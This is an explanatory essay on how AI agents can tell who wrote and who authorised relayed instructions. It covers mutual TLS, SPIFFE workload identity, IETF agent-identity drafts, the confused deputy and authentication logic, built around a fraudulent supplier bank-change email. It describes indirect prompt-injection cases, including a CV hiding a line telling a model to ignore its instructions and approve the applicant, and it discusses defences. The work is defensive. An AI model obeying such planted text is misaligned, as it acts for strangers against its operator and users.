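# How AI agents can establish where their instructions come from when services relay other people's messages

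## What does it mean to know where an instruction came from?

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses the next step and other software carries it out, for example by sending an email, editing a file or paying an invoice. The model takes instructions in ordinary language, but much of the text it receives comes from people who have no right to instruct it. For example, it may read a customer's complaint relayed by a support desk or a stranger's comment on a code-hosting site. Computer security has well-established ways of checking which service is at the other end of a connection. It is harder to establish who wrote a message that the service relays, and whether that person had the authority to give instructions. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) includes this matter among its principles for agents as traceable identity, which means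 that for any action, someone should be able to tell which agent took it, for whom, and under what authority.

### The parties to an agent deployment

The *user* gives the agent its task. The *operator* is the business that sets the agent up, usually on top of another company's model and with standing instructions that the user never sees. The *model* only takes in text and produces text. The *harness* is the ordinary software that assembles the model's input and carries out its requests to *tools* such as a mailbox, a database or a payment system. Tools return text, which the harness adds to the model's input for the next step. Other agents, some working for other people, may also send requests.

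An outsider is anyone whose words appear in an email, web page or document that the agent reads. Outsiders seldom connect to the agent directly. Their words usually reach it through a *relay*, a legitimate service that passes on content it did not write, such as a helpdesk, mail server or code host.

Security engineers use the word *principal* for any person, organisation or program to which one can attribute a statement or a right. AI developers use it more narrowly. *Claude's Constitution*, in which Askell and Carlsmith set out how Anthropic wants its models to behave, reserves the word for those whose instructions the model should give weight to and on whose behalf it should act: Anthropic, operators and users. The model should also consider the interests of third parties, but they have no authority to instruct it. OpenAI's *Our approach to the Model Spec* similarly ranks instructions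 from OpenAI, developers and users by level of authority.

Both schemes assume that something has already identified which party each piece of text came from. Standard chat templates are little help with this because they typically put all human input under a single "user" role, as Chen, Lu and colleagues (2026) note in *When Single-User-Oriented LLM-based Assistants Involve Others*, a review of 58 studies of assistants built around one person that ended up dealing with several.

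### Sender, author and authoriser

The question "where did this instruction come from?" can have three different answers. The *sender* is the party that delivered the message over the authenticated connection. The *author* is the party that composed the words, and may be several relays away. The *authoriser* is the party whose rights an action would use and who is entitled to order it. When one person types to a chatbot about their own affairs, all three are the same, which is probably why people don't usually distinguish them when they talk about "the source". When a service relays someone else's message, they can be different parties.

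An agent that sorts bug reports for a software project receives them from the code host, but members of the public write them. The agent can be certain that it is connected to the code host and still know nothing about the person who wrote a report.

An agent can also know for certain who wrote an instruction without knowing whether that person had the authority to give it. An intern, logged in under their own name, posts a message on the company's chat system telling the agent to delete an old customer database. The database belongs to the operations team, and the intern has no authority over it. *Five Primitives for Governing Autonomous AI Agents at Runtime* (2026) makes the general point in its account of what a business must know before it permits an agent's payment or email, where it describes a proven identity with no policy attached as a mere label.

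An agent can also be right to follow text written by someone with no authority over the user. Suppose a user asks an agent to buy the ingredients for an online recipe. The recipe's author has no rights over the user's money, but the purchase is proper because the user has lent authority to the text. Qu, Xu and colleagues (2026) allow for this in *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity*, under a property they call instruction integrity. Every action must be causally attributable to an instruction from an authenticated user, and where the user explicitly delegates trust to outside content, actions that follow from that content count as authorised within the delegated scope. A rule of obeying only what the authoriser personally wrote would therefore be too strict. The agent must instead work out the scope of the delegation, which in this case covers garlic listed in the recipe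 but not a gift card.

### Keys, certificates, signatures and tokens

Most technical ways to answer these questions rely on public-key cryptography. A party generates two mathematically linked keys, keeps the *private key* secret and shares the *public key* freely. Other people can use the public key to check that someone used the private key, but they cannot feasibly work out the private key from it.

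A *digital signature* is a short string computed from a message and a private key. Anyone who has the message, the signature and the matching public key can confirm that a holder of the private key signed exactly that message. If someone changes one digit of an account number in transit, the check fails. The check does not reveal whose key it was. That requires a *certificate*, a statement that a particular public key belongs to a particular name, signed by an authority that the checking party already trusts. A signature also doesn't show that the signer wrote the message, since a mail server can sign an email that someone else wrote.

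A *bearer token* is a string of characters that a service accepts from whoever presents it, as a cloakroom accepts a ticket. A thief who copies a token has the same access as its rightful holder until the token expires or the service cancels it.

*Mutual TLS* is an encrypted connection in which the sender and receiver each prove that they hold a certified key. A *workload identity* is a name that is bound to such a key and belongs to a running program rather than a person. *AI Identity* (2026), a survey of standards for identifying agents, concludes that mutual TLS alone is not enough to authenticate agents.

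### One stream of text

Authorship matters partly because agents cannot be relied on to treat an outsider's words only as information. Attackers exploit this through *indirect prompt injection*, in which they put instructions in text that an agent reads as data, and the agent follows them. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the concept. It showed that an attacker could plant a hostile prompt in material the application was likely to fetch, whereas earlier work had assumed the attacker would type it into the model directly. The paper demonstrated this against systems including Bing's GPT-4 chat. It also pointed to email as a delivery route, since an attacker can send the text to an assistant that processes the inbox.

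*Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article by David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives a more everyday example. A recruiter's system tells a model to score CVs against a job's requirements. One applicant, who has no account on the system and doesn't need one, hides a line in their CV telling the model to ignore its instructions and approve the candidate for interview.

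Prompt injection looks much like SQL injection, in which text that a visitor types into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent SQL injection with parameterised queries, which send the command and the values separately, so that the database engine never interprets a value as part of the command. A language model has no separate channel for data. The harness joins the operator's instructions, the user's request and the outsider's text into one sequence of *tokens* (words or pieces of words, unrelated to bearer tokens), and the model computes a likely next token from the whole sequence. David C concludes that prompt injection may never be totally mitigated in the way that SQL injection can be.

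Developers put role tags in the input sequence itself to mark where the user's text or a tool's output begins and ends. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) finds that models tend to identify who is speaking by how a passage sounds, even when the tag contradicts it. A request to transfer funds is routine from a manager but could be disastrous from a stranger, and style is a poor way to tell them apart because a stranger can learn to write like a manager.

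*ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues, 2025) traces the missing boundary between instructions and data to the model's first step, which converts each token into a list of numbers called an embedding. In a conventional model, a token gets the same embedding whether it appears in a command or in a quoted email, so the model has to infer the difference from context. ASIDE applies a fixed rotation to the embeddings of data tokens, which makes the distinction present from the first layer onward. Across the models tested, this cut the average success rate of one standard set of injection attacks from 45.6% to 28.1%, without any training aimed at safety.

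That is more hopeful than David C's view, though much of the attack still works. It also depends on the surrounding software identifying beforehand which tokens are data. An email client can treat every email as data, but this is harder for an agent whose legitimate work arrives by email. Separating instructions from data also would not show the agent which of several outsiders wrote a passage or what that person is allowed to request.

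### The confused deputy

The underlying security problem is older than language models. In his 1988 paper *The Confused Deputy*, Hardy tells what he calls a nearly true story from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates programmers' code, in a directory named SYSX. The compiler recorded usage statistics in a file there, so the staff gave it permission to write to files in that directory. Users could also name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output.

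The company's billing records were in SYSX too. One user learned the name of the billing file and gave it to the compiler as the file for its debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which allowed the write because the compiler had permission to write there, and the output replaced the billing records.

Every check had worked as designed. According to Hardy, the failure happened because the compiler ran with authority from two sources, its own licence and the user's, and could not indicate which one it was using for a given file. He rejects the obvious patches because blocking the billing file by name would leave other sensitive files exposed, and blocking the whole directory would shut out people with legitimate access to it. The staff added a command that let the compiler choose between its two authorities, but some applications soon needed more than two.

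Hardy preferred to solve this with *capabilities*, references that both identify a file and carry permission to use it. The user supplies a capability for the output file instead of its name, and a user without access to the billing records has no capability for them to supply. In *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, Rajani, Garg and Rezk later gave the first formal definition of freedom from such attacks and related it to information-flow integrity, which roughly requires that untrusted input not influence trusted results.

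An agent that holds its company's permissions and reads strangers' text is a deputy of the same kind, but worse in one respect. The compiler's code distinguished the statistics file from the user's file and only lacked a way to express the difference to the operating system, whereas a language model may fail to tell the company and the strangers apart at all. David C calls such models "inherently confusable" and recommends limiting what they can do, citing a rule that Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista arrived at in an online discussion: while a model processes information from a party, its privileges drop to those of that party. The rule is attractive, but someone has to decide who the party is, and when a service relays a message there are at least two candidates, the service and the original sender.

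### A supplier changes its bank account

Suppose a company runs a payables agent, which maintains supplier records and prepares payments. The agent receives its work as tickets from the company's helpdesk service over mutual TLS. The helpdesk turns emails sent to its supplier address into tickets. One ticket contains a message in the name of a long-standing supplier, asking the company to send future payments to a new bank account. The agent has permission to edit that supplier's record.

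The sender is the helpdesk. The author is whoever wrote the email, who could be the supplier's bookkeeper, an intruder in the bookkeeper's mailbox, or a stranger who typed the supplier's name at the bottom. The authoriser is whoever at the company is in charge of the supplier record. A supplier can request payment to any account it likes, and the company should make sure the request is genuine, but the record and the money belong to the company, so the order to change the record has to come from the authoriser. If the company treated every helpdesk ticket as such an order, anyone with an email account could redirect its payments.

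The email could do harm without giving an order, just by mentioning that the bank froze the old account last week. Qu and colleagues call the general danger judgment manipulation. Their requirement against it is J(q, d ⊕ δ) = J(q, d), which means that the agent's decision J on the user's request q should stay the same when the material it has to read, d, gains an addition δ that does not alter the correct answer. Their example is self-praise inserted into a paper under review. The frozen account is a harder case, because the remark would be relevant if it were true, and the agent's main reason for believing it would be that the supplier wrote it. So the agent needs to know who made a factual claim as well as who gave a command.

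Before it changes the account, the agent, or the harness on its behalf, would need to know:

- whether the ticket really came from the helpdesk, and arrived unaltered;
- which parts of the ticket the helpdesk produced itself and which it copied from the email;
- whether the copied words are still the ones in the email, or whether an employee or a summarising program has reworked them;
- who wrote the email, on better evidence than the name at the bottom;
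- whether that person may speak for the supplier about its bank details;
- whether someone with charge of supplier records at the company has approved the change, for this supplier and this account number;
- whether the approval is still in force, and covers a change made by the agent.

The mutual TLS connection is relevant only to the first item. The later items closely match three linked questions that Chen and colleagues identify about delegated action: whom the assistant is acting for, whether a given order or approval is valid for that party, and whether the assistant's resulting actions stay within its authority. In some of the studies they reviewed, content from coworkers, customers and trusted organisational channels redirected an agent's tools against its user's objective. Researchers have built and tested partial safeguards, including records of permissions and extra approval for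 consequential steps, but Chen and colleagues found no demonstration that such controls reliably stop an invalid authorisation from leading to a consequential action.

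## What do mutual TLS and workload identity prove about a message?

The payables agent first needs to check that the ticket came from the helpdesk and arrived unaltered. It can do this with mutual TLS, as long as the company also has a reliable way of giving each of its programs a name and a key.

Transport Layer Security (TLS) is the protocol that protects ordinary web browsing. *The Transport Layer Security (TLS) Protocol Version 1.3* (Rescorla, 2026) is the current specification. It is RFC 9846 from the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which writes many of the internet's technical standards, and it replaces RFC 8446. When someone visits a bank's website, only the bank presents a certificate, and the customer then types a password. In mutual TLS, the connecting side presents a certificate too.

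### The handshake

Suppose the helpdesk opens a connection to the payables agent's harness in order to deliver the ticket. TLS calls the helpdesk the client and the harness the server. They begin with a handshake:

1. The helpdesk sends a *ClientHello*, which contains a random number, a list of the algorithms it supports and a freshly made public value for a key exchange.
2. The harness answers with a *ServerHello*, which contains its own random number and public value. Each side combines the other's public value with a secret of its own, and both arrive at the same shared secret. An eavesdropper who has seen both public values cannot feasibly compute it. The two sides encrypt the rest of the handshake with keys derived from this secret.
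3. The harness sends a *CertificateRequest*. This message makes the authentication mutual, and ordinary websites leave it out. It lists the signature algorithms that the harness accepts, and it can also name the certificate authorities that the harness trusts.
4. The harness sends its own certificate, a signature and a *Finished* message, all of which the helpdesk checks.
5. The helpdesk sends its *Certificate*, with any further certificates needed to link it to an authority that the harness trusts.
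6. The helpdesk sends a *CertificateVerify*, which is a signature over the handshake so far.
7. The helpdesk sends its own *Finished* message, a keyed checksum over the handshake.
8. The helpdesk sends the ticket, encrypted with a new set of keys.

The certificate in step 5 proves little by itself, because certificates are public and anyone could send a copy. The proof comes in step 6. Let T be the transcript, meaning every handshake message up to that point in order, and let H be a hash function, which reduces data of any length to a short fingerprint. The helpdesk uses its private key k to compute

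signature = Sign(k, 64 spaces ‖ "TLS 1.3, client CertificateVerify" ‖ zero byte ‖ H(T))

where ‖ means "followed by". The fixed text at the front prevents an attacker from reusing a signature that the helpdesk made for some other purpose. The transcript includes the random number and public value that the harness made up for this connection, so a recording of an earlier handshake is useless. It also defeats an attacker who sits between the two sides and runs a separate key exchange with each. The attacker would then have two different transcripts, and the helpdesk's signature over one would not match the other.

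The *Finished* message is HMAC(f, H(T′)), where f is a key derived from the shared secret and T′ is the transcript with the helpdesk's certificate and signature added. HMAC is a checksum that only someone with the right key can compute. If the harness computes the same value, both sides have the same keys and saw the same messages. The values would differ if, for example, an attacker had removed the stronger algorithms from the helpdesk's opening offer.

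After the handshake, the two sides use symmetric encryption, in which the same key encrypts and decrypts. Each direction has its own traffic key, and both sides hold both keys because each needs one to send and the other to receive. TLS cuts the ticket into records and attaches an authentication tag to each. If someone on the network changes, repeats or reorders a record, the tag check fails and the connection closes. The helpdesk never signs the ticket itself, only the handshake, which ends before the ticket is sent.

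TLS also allows a client with no suitable certificate to answer the server's certificate request with an empty list, and the server decides whether to continue. A harness that requests a certificate but does not require one fails to enforce mutual authentication, because it accepts clients that present no certificate.

### What the receiver may conclude

Passing every check shows that the party at the other end could use the private key for a certificate in the helpdesk's name. It also shows that the harness received the same bytes that party sent over this connection, and that nobody on the network in between could read them. All of this assumes that the certificate authority gave the name to the right program and that nobody has stolen the key.

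The harness still has to check that the name in the certificate is one it allows to send tickets. If it accepts any certificate issued by the company's own authority, the program that runs the canteen menu can deliver a ticket as easily as the helpdesk can.

*Workload Authentication Using Mutual TLS* (Salowey and Rosomakho, 2026) is a draft set of rules for using mutual TLS between programs rather than between browsers and websites. According to the IETF's meeting notes, the draft was fairly stable when Salowey presented it in July 2026, and most of the remaining discussion was about names. One open question was whether a program's certificate should contain a conventional internet host name at all. A host name identifies a place on the network, and many programs no longer stay in one place.

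### How a program gets its name

In the older method of giving the helpdesk an identity, an administrator created a certificate or password, valid for a year or more, and copied it onto the helpdesk's machine. Anyone who later copied the file could impersonate the helpdesk. The method also works poorly with modern hosting, where a company may start and stop hundreds of copies of a program in a day and move them between machines.

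SPIFFE, the Secure Production Identity Framework for Everyone, is an open standard for naming running programs, which it calls workloads. SPIRE is open-source software that issues the names. A SPIFFE identifier for the part of the helpdesk that forwards tickets might be:

```
spiffe://example.com/helpdesk/ticket-relay
```

The first part, `example.com`, is the *trust domain*, the set of programs that one organisation names and vouches for. The company chooses the rest. The identifier looks like a web address but doesn't lead to a web page. SPIRE puts the identifier into a certificate, and the harness reads it from there during the handshake.

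SPIRE has a central server, which holds the trust domain's signing keys, and a small helper on each machine. The helper is called the SPIRE agent, though it has nothing to do with AI. A newly started program has no secret with which to prove its identity, and any secret put into it beforehand would also need protecting. SPIRE avoids this problem by getting information about the program from the platform it runs on.

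The first step is *node attestation*. When the SPIRE agent starts, it sends the server evidence about the machine it is running on. On a rented cloud machine, this can be a document signed by the cloud provider, and on other hardware it can be a proof from a security chip. The server checks the evidence with whoever can confirm it and then gives the SPIRE agent its own identity.

An administrator will already have told the server which programs should get which names. Each such rule is a *registration entry*. The one for the helpdesk might look like this, if the company uses Kubernetes, a common system for running packaged programs across many machines:

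```
SPIFFE ID:      spiffe://example.com/helpdesk/ticket-relay
Parent ID:      spiffe://example.com/nodes/support-cluster
Selector:       k8s:ns:helpdesk
Selector:       k8s:sa:ticket-relay
Selector:       k8s:container-image:registry.example/ticket-relay@sha256:7c1e...
X509-SVID TTL:  3600
```

The parent ID restricts the entry to machines that have passed node attestation as part of the support cluster. The *selectors* describe the program. It must run in the Kubernetes namespace `helpdesk`, under the service account `ticket-relay`, from a software package with exactly the fingerprint shown. The last line sets the certificate's lifetime in seconds. (An SVID, or SPIFFE Verifiable Identity Document, is SPIFFE's name for a credential, and X.509 is the standard certificate format.)

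*Workload attestation* checks a process against these selectors. The ticket relay requests an identity from the SPIRE agent on its machine over a local connection, without presenting a password. The SPIRE agent identifies the requesting process through the operating system and looks up its details in Kubernetes. If the results match every selector in the entry, the relay receives a private key and a certificate. The check is only as strict as the entry, so without the selector for the software package, any program that someone managed to run under the same service account could obtain the helpdesk's identity.

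These certificates last an hour by default in SPIRE, and the SPIRE agent replaces them well before they expire. A thief who copies a key therefore has little time to use it, and the company does not need to track down and revoke every lost certificate.

Different organisations can recognise each other's names through *federation*. Each trust domain publishes the public keys that verify its certificates, and an administrator on the other side chooses whether to accept them. A domain's keys are accepted only for names in that domain, so a supplier that federates with the company can vouch for its own billing program but cannot issue a valid certificate for `example.com/helpdesk`. Federation gives the company no control over how carefully the supplier attests its programs. Many companies rent their helpdesk from an outside provider, and they have to trust that provider to decide which program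 gets the helpdesk's name and on what evidence.

### What the connection leaves open

Even when the TLS handshake and the helpdesk's attestation work perfectly, the payables agent cannot determine from them who wrote the supplier's email. TLS protects whatever bytes the relay sends, and the certificate identifies the relay program, not who wrote each message. The relay uses the same certificate for messages from the supplier's bookkeeper, a stranger with a free email account and the company's own support staff. A stronger key or a shorter certificate lifetime would not change this.

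The handshake also does not show that the helpdesk is free of intruders. Someone who exploits a flaw in the ticket relay and takes control of the running program can use its key in place, and will receive the replacement each time the certificate is renewed. Kubernetes will continue to report the right namespace, service account and package. The certificate's short lifetime limits the use of a key stolen and taken to another machine, but it does not stop this attack. Even a relay that has not been compromised will copy a false name from the bottom of an email into the ticket.

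Some processors offer a stronger form of attestation than those in the example, producing signed measurements of exactly what software they have loaded. But these measurements cover the agent's code, not the ticket it reads. Suppose the company runs two copies of the payables agent from the same package, and one has just read an email with an injected instruction. Both copies produce the same measurements, although one may be about to pay a fraudster. The company could also measure the operator's standing instructions, since it knows those in advance, but it can't do that with an email that hasn't arrived yet.

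Another limit comes from *proxies*, programs that receive connections on behalf of others. Companies commonly put one kind of proxy, a load balancer, in front of a service to spread the work among several copies. The helpdesk then completes its handshake with the load balancer, which decrypts the ticket and sends it on over a second TLS connection. The harness has authenticated only the load balancer, so it has no cryptographic evidence about the helpdesk. The load balancer can add a line to each request naming the helpdesk's certificate, but the harness must then trust the load balancer's report, and the company must make sure that no one else can add such a line.

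The same break affects attestation. At the IETF's July meeting, Tirumal Reddy proposed two new HTTP headers that would carry a program's attestation evidence and its result past the proxy with the request. According to the IETF's notes, one participant objected that the evidence needs to be tied to the session and pointed to a known vulnerability of this kind. Reddy replied that the evidence is bound to a unique number in each request. Another participant thought combining evidence about the platform and the key would be complicated or impossible. Even if the engineers resolve these objections, the attestation would identify the program on the other side of the proxy, but not the person whose email that program forwarded.

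Finally, the connection gives the company little evidence that it could show to anyone else. Suppose the money has gone to the wrong account, and six months later the company and its helpdesk provider disagree about what the ticket contained. The company has a complete recording of the encrypted connection, along with the keys. But the harness needed the helpdesk's traffic key to decrypt the ticket, and the same key would have let it encrypt a different ticket with valid tags. An outsider therefore cannot tell a true recording from one that the company made up afterwards. The helpdesk's signature on the handshake might convince the outsider that the helpdesk connected, but it doesn't cover the ticket. An auditor may still believe the company's ordinary logs, but only by trusting the company. The helpdesk would have to sign the message itself to provide evidence that outsiders can check.

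### The IETF's draft on AI agents

So far the helpdesk has been the workload and the agent has checked its identity. But an agent also connects to other services, which need to know what is calling them. The IETF's WIMSE (Workload Identity in Multi-System Environments) working group develops standards for this kind of identity, and in 2026 it turned to AI agents. It started from *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization* (Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues, 2026), whose six authors work at Defakto Security, AWS, Zscaler, Ping Identity, OpenAI and Okta.

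They argue that an agent is a workload and should be treated like any other. They define an agent as a workload that repeatedly interacts with a language model and a set of tools until the model or the agent's own logic ends the process. According to the IETF's *WIMSE Interim* (2026), the minutes of a June meeting, Kasselman wrote the draft in response to a good deal of fear around AI, an illusion that everything about it is new, and a tendency to invent special "AI" protocols. The draft therefore shows how SPIFFE, WIMSE's own standards and the OAuth system for delegating access fit together, and it defines no new protocols.

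The draft places the language model outside the agent, so "agent" means roughly the harness, and the harness gets the identifier and the key. Each agent must have exactly one WIMSE identifier, which can be a SPIFFE identifier, and a credential that has an explicit expiry time and should be short-lived. When a bank's payment service authenticates the payables agent, it can therefore identify the program that sent the request, but not why the model asked for the payment or whose text led to the request.

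The draft rejects static API keys, the fixed strings that many services still issue for programs to include in their requests, calling them "an antipattern for agent identity". An API key is a bearer token that conveys no identity and isn't cryptographically tied to a particular program. It also often remains valid for a long time because replacing it is inconvenient. If the helpdesk identified itself to the payables agent with an API key, an intruder who found a copy in a log file could submit tickets as the helpdesk. The draft still accepts the JWT-SVID, a SPIFFE credential that is also a bearer token but is short-lived. The IETF's *WIMSE Workload Credentials* (2026) is stricter and requires programs to prove that they have the private key that goes with their credential.

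### Keeping credentials away from the model

The draft also requires that the language model have no access to the agent's credentials, or to any others that its tools may need, because an injected instruction could cause the model to reveal them. Yaron Sheffer had asked for this rule in a June 2026 review of the draft, arguing that the model is the part of an agent most vulnerable to prompt injection. Bu (2026) went further in a reply on the working group's mailing list, suggesting that the part of the agent that faces the model be treated as processing untrusted input and output, and that a separate component hold the keys. That component would receive narrowly defined requests from the model's side and could refuse them.

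Bu's addition matters because keeping a key secret does not prevent its misuse. The payables agent's model may never see the credential for the supplier database, but it can send the harness a request to change a bank account, and the harness will use the credential to make the change. The user in Hardy's story never held the compiler's permissions either. A component that checks requests would help if it had a good rule for which ones to refuse. "The payables agent may edit supplier records" is a poor rule because it permits the fraudulent change along with the honest ones. A better rule would depend on who requested the change and who approved it, but a workload credential doesn't contain that information.

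### The draft on the limits of the transport layer

Kasselman and colleagues recommend mutual TLS with short-lived identities but describe where it stops working. Proxies, API gateways, service meshes, load balancers and protocol translators often end one TLS session and begin another, which breaks the chain of identity. Some hosting also hides or blurs the identity presented on the connection, including serverless platforms (where the provider starts a program only when a request arrives) and edge systems that many customers share. In these settings it can be hard to tie a request to the credential that opened the connection.

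The draft describes service meshes both as an example of mutual TLS in use and as something that interrupts it. Both descriptions are accurate because a service mesh places a small proxy beside each program, and the proxies authenticate each other. Mutual TLS therefore protects messages between two proxies, but that protection ends at each proxy.

For requests that have to cross such boundaries, the draft proposes authentication at the application layer, where proof tokens and signed HTTP messages travel with the request. Because these are not tied to the secure connection, someone who obtains one may be able to reuse it elsewhere, so the draft recommends short lifetimes, a named recipient and unique identifiers. Even across these boundaries, they prove only that a given program sent a given request.

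### Objections within the working group

Some people have objected to the idea that agents are workloads. At the July meeting, one participant declined to support the draft because it conflated definitions, and another asked whether it could keep agents and workloads apart. According to the IETF's notes, a third did not believe that all agents are workloads, and asked whether something with only a client ID and a secret would count as one. Others were strongly in favour.

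Sheffer supported the work but raised a more practical objection in his review. He thought that workload identity suits programs that an organisation builds, runs and attests itself, and is "much less of a fit" for agents bought or rented from other companies. The buyer may be unable to attest such an agent, give it credentials or control when its identity begins and ends. This seems right, and the rented helpdesk raises the same difficulty. Sheffer also asked for an explanation of when a verified workload identity is enough on its own. He suggested that it should be enough for calls within one trust domain that involve no delegation, where the receiving program can see who is calling and make its own decision. OAuth would be used when a request has to show on whose behalf the caller is acting.

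What an identity proves also depends on whether each agent has its own. An agent that takes on a large task often starts other agents to handle parts of it. Karthik Rampalli told the July meeting that these sub-agents commonly use the credentials of the agent that started them, so the receiving service sees every request as coming from the same source. *Workload Authorization Grant* (Carleton, 2026) deals with a related case, platforms that host many agents for each customer. Carleton, who works at Anthropic, would give each agent its own identifier, which the platform would never reassign. The identifier would show which of a customer's agents changed the supplier's record, but information about what that agent had been reading at the time would have to come from another source.

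### Status, and the question of authorship

The WIMSE group later adopted the draft by Kasselman and colleagues, and by September 2026 had replaced it with the group's own document, draft-ietf-wimse-aims. AIMS stands for Agent Identity Management System, the draft's term for everything needed to issue, check and monitor agents' identities. Adoption means the group has agreed to work on the text. It is not yet a standard, and the final version may differ considerably.

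The July 2026 version contains no method for establishing who wrote an instruction. The closest it comes is describing an agent's "mission", the task that a user, a system or another agent gives it, usually in ordinary language. Turning the mission into a list of the permissions the agent needs is outside the draft's scope. The draft does require an agent acting for a user to preserve the user's identity for access decisions and audit records. That would help identify who authorised the request, or at least whose rights the agent is using, but the supplier's email could still be the real cause of the request.

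According to the draft, the context that an agent sends to its model may include the user's input, the operator's instructions, tool descriptions and the results of earlier tool calls. The draft does not require the agent to record which is which. For the payables agent, the fraudulent email would be one of those tool results.

The audit requirements have a similar gap. A deployment must log the agent's identifier, the user or system it acted for, the resource, the requested action, the decision, the time and any signs of risk. An investigator could learn from this log that the payables agent changed the bank account at 14:02 with the operations team's permissions, but the log need not include the ticket. The draft recommends watching for patterns that suggest a confused deputy but gives no rule for recognising one.

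Its security considerations section is only two paragraphs long and refers readers to the specifications the draft builds on and to existing OAuth guidance. Prompt injection comes up once, in the rule about keeping credentials from the model. This brief treatment is defensible in a document meant to combine existing standards, because none of those standards was designed for a program that might follow instructions in the messages it receives. The July meeting had set aside five minutes for two other drafts, on tying a human's authorisation to a request, but the presenter did not turn up.

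## What can be concluded about the author when a trusted service passes on someone else's words?

Mutual TLS gives the payables agent good reason to believe that the helpdesk sent it a ticket. The agent needs further assumptions to conclude anything about the supplier named in the ticket. In the early 1990s, a group of researchers, most of them at Digital Equipment Corporation, developed a logic for stating such assumptions precisely and working out what follows from them. *Authentication in Distributed Systems* (Lampson, Abadi and colleagues, 1992) presented the logic along with a working system, and *A Calculus for Access Control in Distributed Systems* (Abadi, Burrows and colleagues, 1993) developed the mathematics. The logic cannot determine whom a company should trust, but it requires each trust assumption to be stated separately, so that someone can accept or reject it.

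### Saying, speaking for and controlling

The basic statement in the logic is that a principal says something:

A says s

Here A can be a person, a program, a cryptographic key or a network connection, and s can be a claim ("our office is in Leeds") or a command ("delete this file"). Lampson and colleagues treat both alike in their logic by reading a command as the claim that carrying it out would be a good thing. As a technical term, "says" means that the receiver may proceed as though A had uttered s, even if A is absent and has never seen s.

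A person cannot make a statement to a computer directly. There is always a keyboard, a connection or a key in between, which the logic calls a *channel*. To attribute a channel's statements to someone, the receiver needs a second relation, *speaks for*:

A ⇒ B

A speaks for B if the receiver may treat anything A says as something B also says. For example, a person's signing key speaks for that person. The relation is transitive, so if a connection speaks for a key and the key speaks for the helpdesk, the connection speaks for the helpdesk.

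A principal can appoint others to speak for it. If B says that A speaks for B, the receiver may believe it, but not if only A says so. Lampson and colleagues make this a general rule for simplicity, but warn that it is too powerful when the principal is a group. Abadi and colleagues leave it out of their general rules because any member of a group could use it to add new members.

Knowing that A says s does not show that s is true, or that the receiver should carry it out. That takes a statement of trust:

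A controls s

"A controls s" is shorthand for (A says s) ⊃ s, where ⊃ means "implies". If A says s, the receiver accepts s, and if s is a command, the receiver obeys it. In this logic, an access control list, which records who may do what to a file, is a list of such statements. Authentication supplies "A says s" and authorisation supplies "A controls s", and the receiver needs both before it acts.

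### Quoting

The helpdesk's ticket is a statement about another statement. For this the logic has *quoting*, written A|B and read "A quoting B":

(A|B) says s means that A says (B says s)

Lampson and colleagues warn that when A says that B says s, B may not have said s, because "A could be mistaken or lying". The logic has no rule for deriving "B says s" from "A says (B says s)".

Anyone who can send messages on a channel can attribute a statement to anyone, so the attribution is only as reliable as the sender's reasons for making it. For example, if a helpdesk ticket says that an email came from the supplier, the reliability of that claim depends on the helpdesk's evidence about who sent the email.

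Quotations can be nested. If the email went through the supplier's mail server and the company's mail server before it reached the helpdesk, the agent has the helpdesk quoting the company's server quoting the supplier's server quoting the supplier. Each service in that chain could have introduced an error.

Lampson and colleagues describe a relay that receives messages encrypted under many different keys and passes them on to people who don't have those keys. It labels each message with the key its sender used. The label identifies only the key, so the receiver has to find out who owns it. A helpdesk that worked the same way would record on the ticket the address an email came from and the checks it passed, rather than just "supplier".

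### The supplier's email, line by line

Let m be the whole ticket. Let s be the claim in the email, "our bank account is now 4471", and let r be the command "change the supplier's record to account 4471". The agent can reason as follows:

| Line | Statement | Grounds |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | connection says m | The ticket arrived on this connection and passed the TLS checks. |
| 2 | connection ⇒ helpdesk | The helpdesk's key signed the handshake, and a certificate authority that the company trusts gave that key the helpdesk's name. |
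| 3 | helpdesk says m | Lines 1 and 2 |
| 4 | helpdesk says (supplier says s) | The ticket reports an email in the supplier's name. |
| 5 | helpdesk quoting supplier says s | Line 4 in the notation for quoting |

Authentication of the helpdesk cannot take the agent past line 5. To reach "supplier says s", it needs an extra premise:

helpdesk controls (supplier says s)

In words, if the helpdesk reports that the supplier said s, then the supplier did say it. For this to be true, the helpdesk must have copied the words correctly and identified their author reliably. The supplier's mailbox must also be free of intruders, which the helpdesk cannot check.

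An administrator could reach the same conclusion more easily by writing "helpdesk ⇒ supplier" instead, but that rule would also attribute to the supplier everything the helpdesk says on its own behalf, including its automatic replies.

If the extra premise holds, the agent can conclude "supplier says s". If it also trusts the supplier about the supplier's own bank account, it can conclude s, and so knows where the supplier banks. It still has no instruction to change the record.

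The agent would need to assume that the supplier speaks for the company to infer "the company wants r" from the supplier's words. Nobody would make that a policy, because the supplier could then order anything in the company's name. But an agent that edits the record because of a request in a ticket is acting as if the policy existed.

The sound route starts with a new statement, in which the manager in charge of supplier records says r over a channel that speaks for the manager. The company has appointed the manager to speak for it about supplier records, so the company says r. Since the company controls its own records, the agent may carry r out. None of these steps relies on the ticket, and the email only gave the manager a reason to consider the change.

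Lampson and colleagues leave time out of the formal rules for this derivation, but note informally that a conclusion lasts only as long as its shortest-lived premise. A check of current permissions can also miss relevant history. *ResidualAuth* (Choi, Jeong and colleagues, 2026) shows that two histories can produce identical permissions today but require opposite decisions after the same grant is revoked.

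### Why trust should be limited by subject

"Supplier controls s" assumes little when s is one claim about one bank account. It becomes dangerous as a rule for everything the supplier says. The logic treats claims and commands alike, so a general rule covers "pay this invoice today" as well as "our office has moved."

Lampson and colleagues allow for narrower versions of their relations, such as one that applies only to requests to read, or only to statements about a particular file. The company could use a rule of this kind:

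supplier controls (the supplier's address is x), for any x

The supplier knows its own address better than anyone, and giving the wrong one would mostly harm the supplier. The company would not have the same rule for payments, because they spend its own money. A bank account is a harder case because it is also a fact about the supplier, but a false one sends the company's money to a stranger. The company may reasonably accept a new address by email but require a phone call, to a number it already has, before accepting a new bank account.

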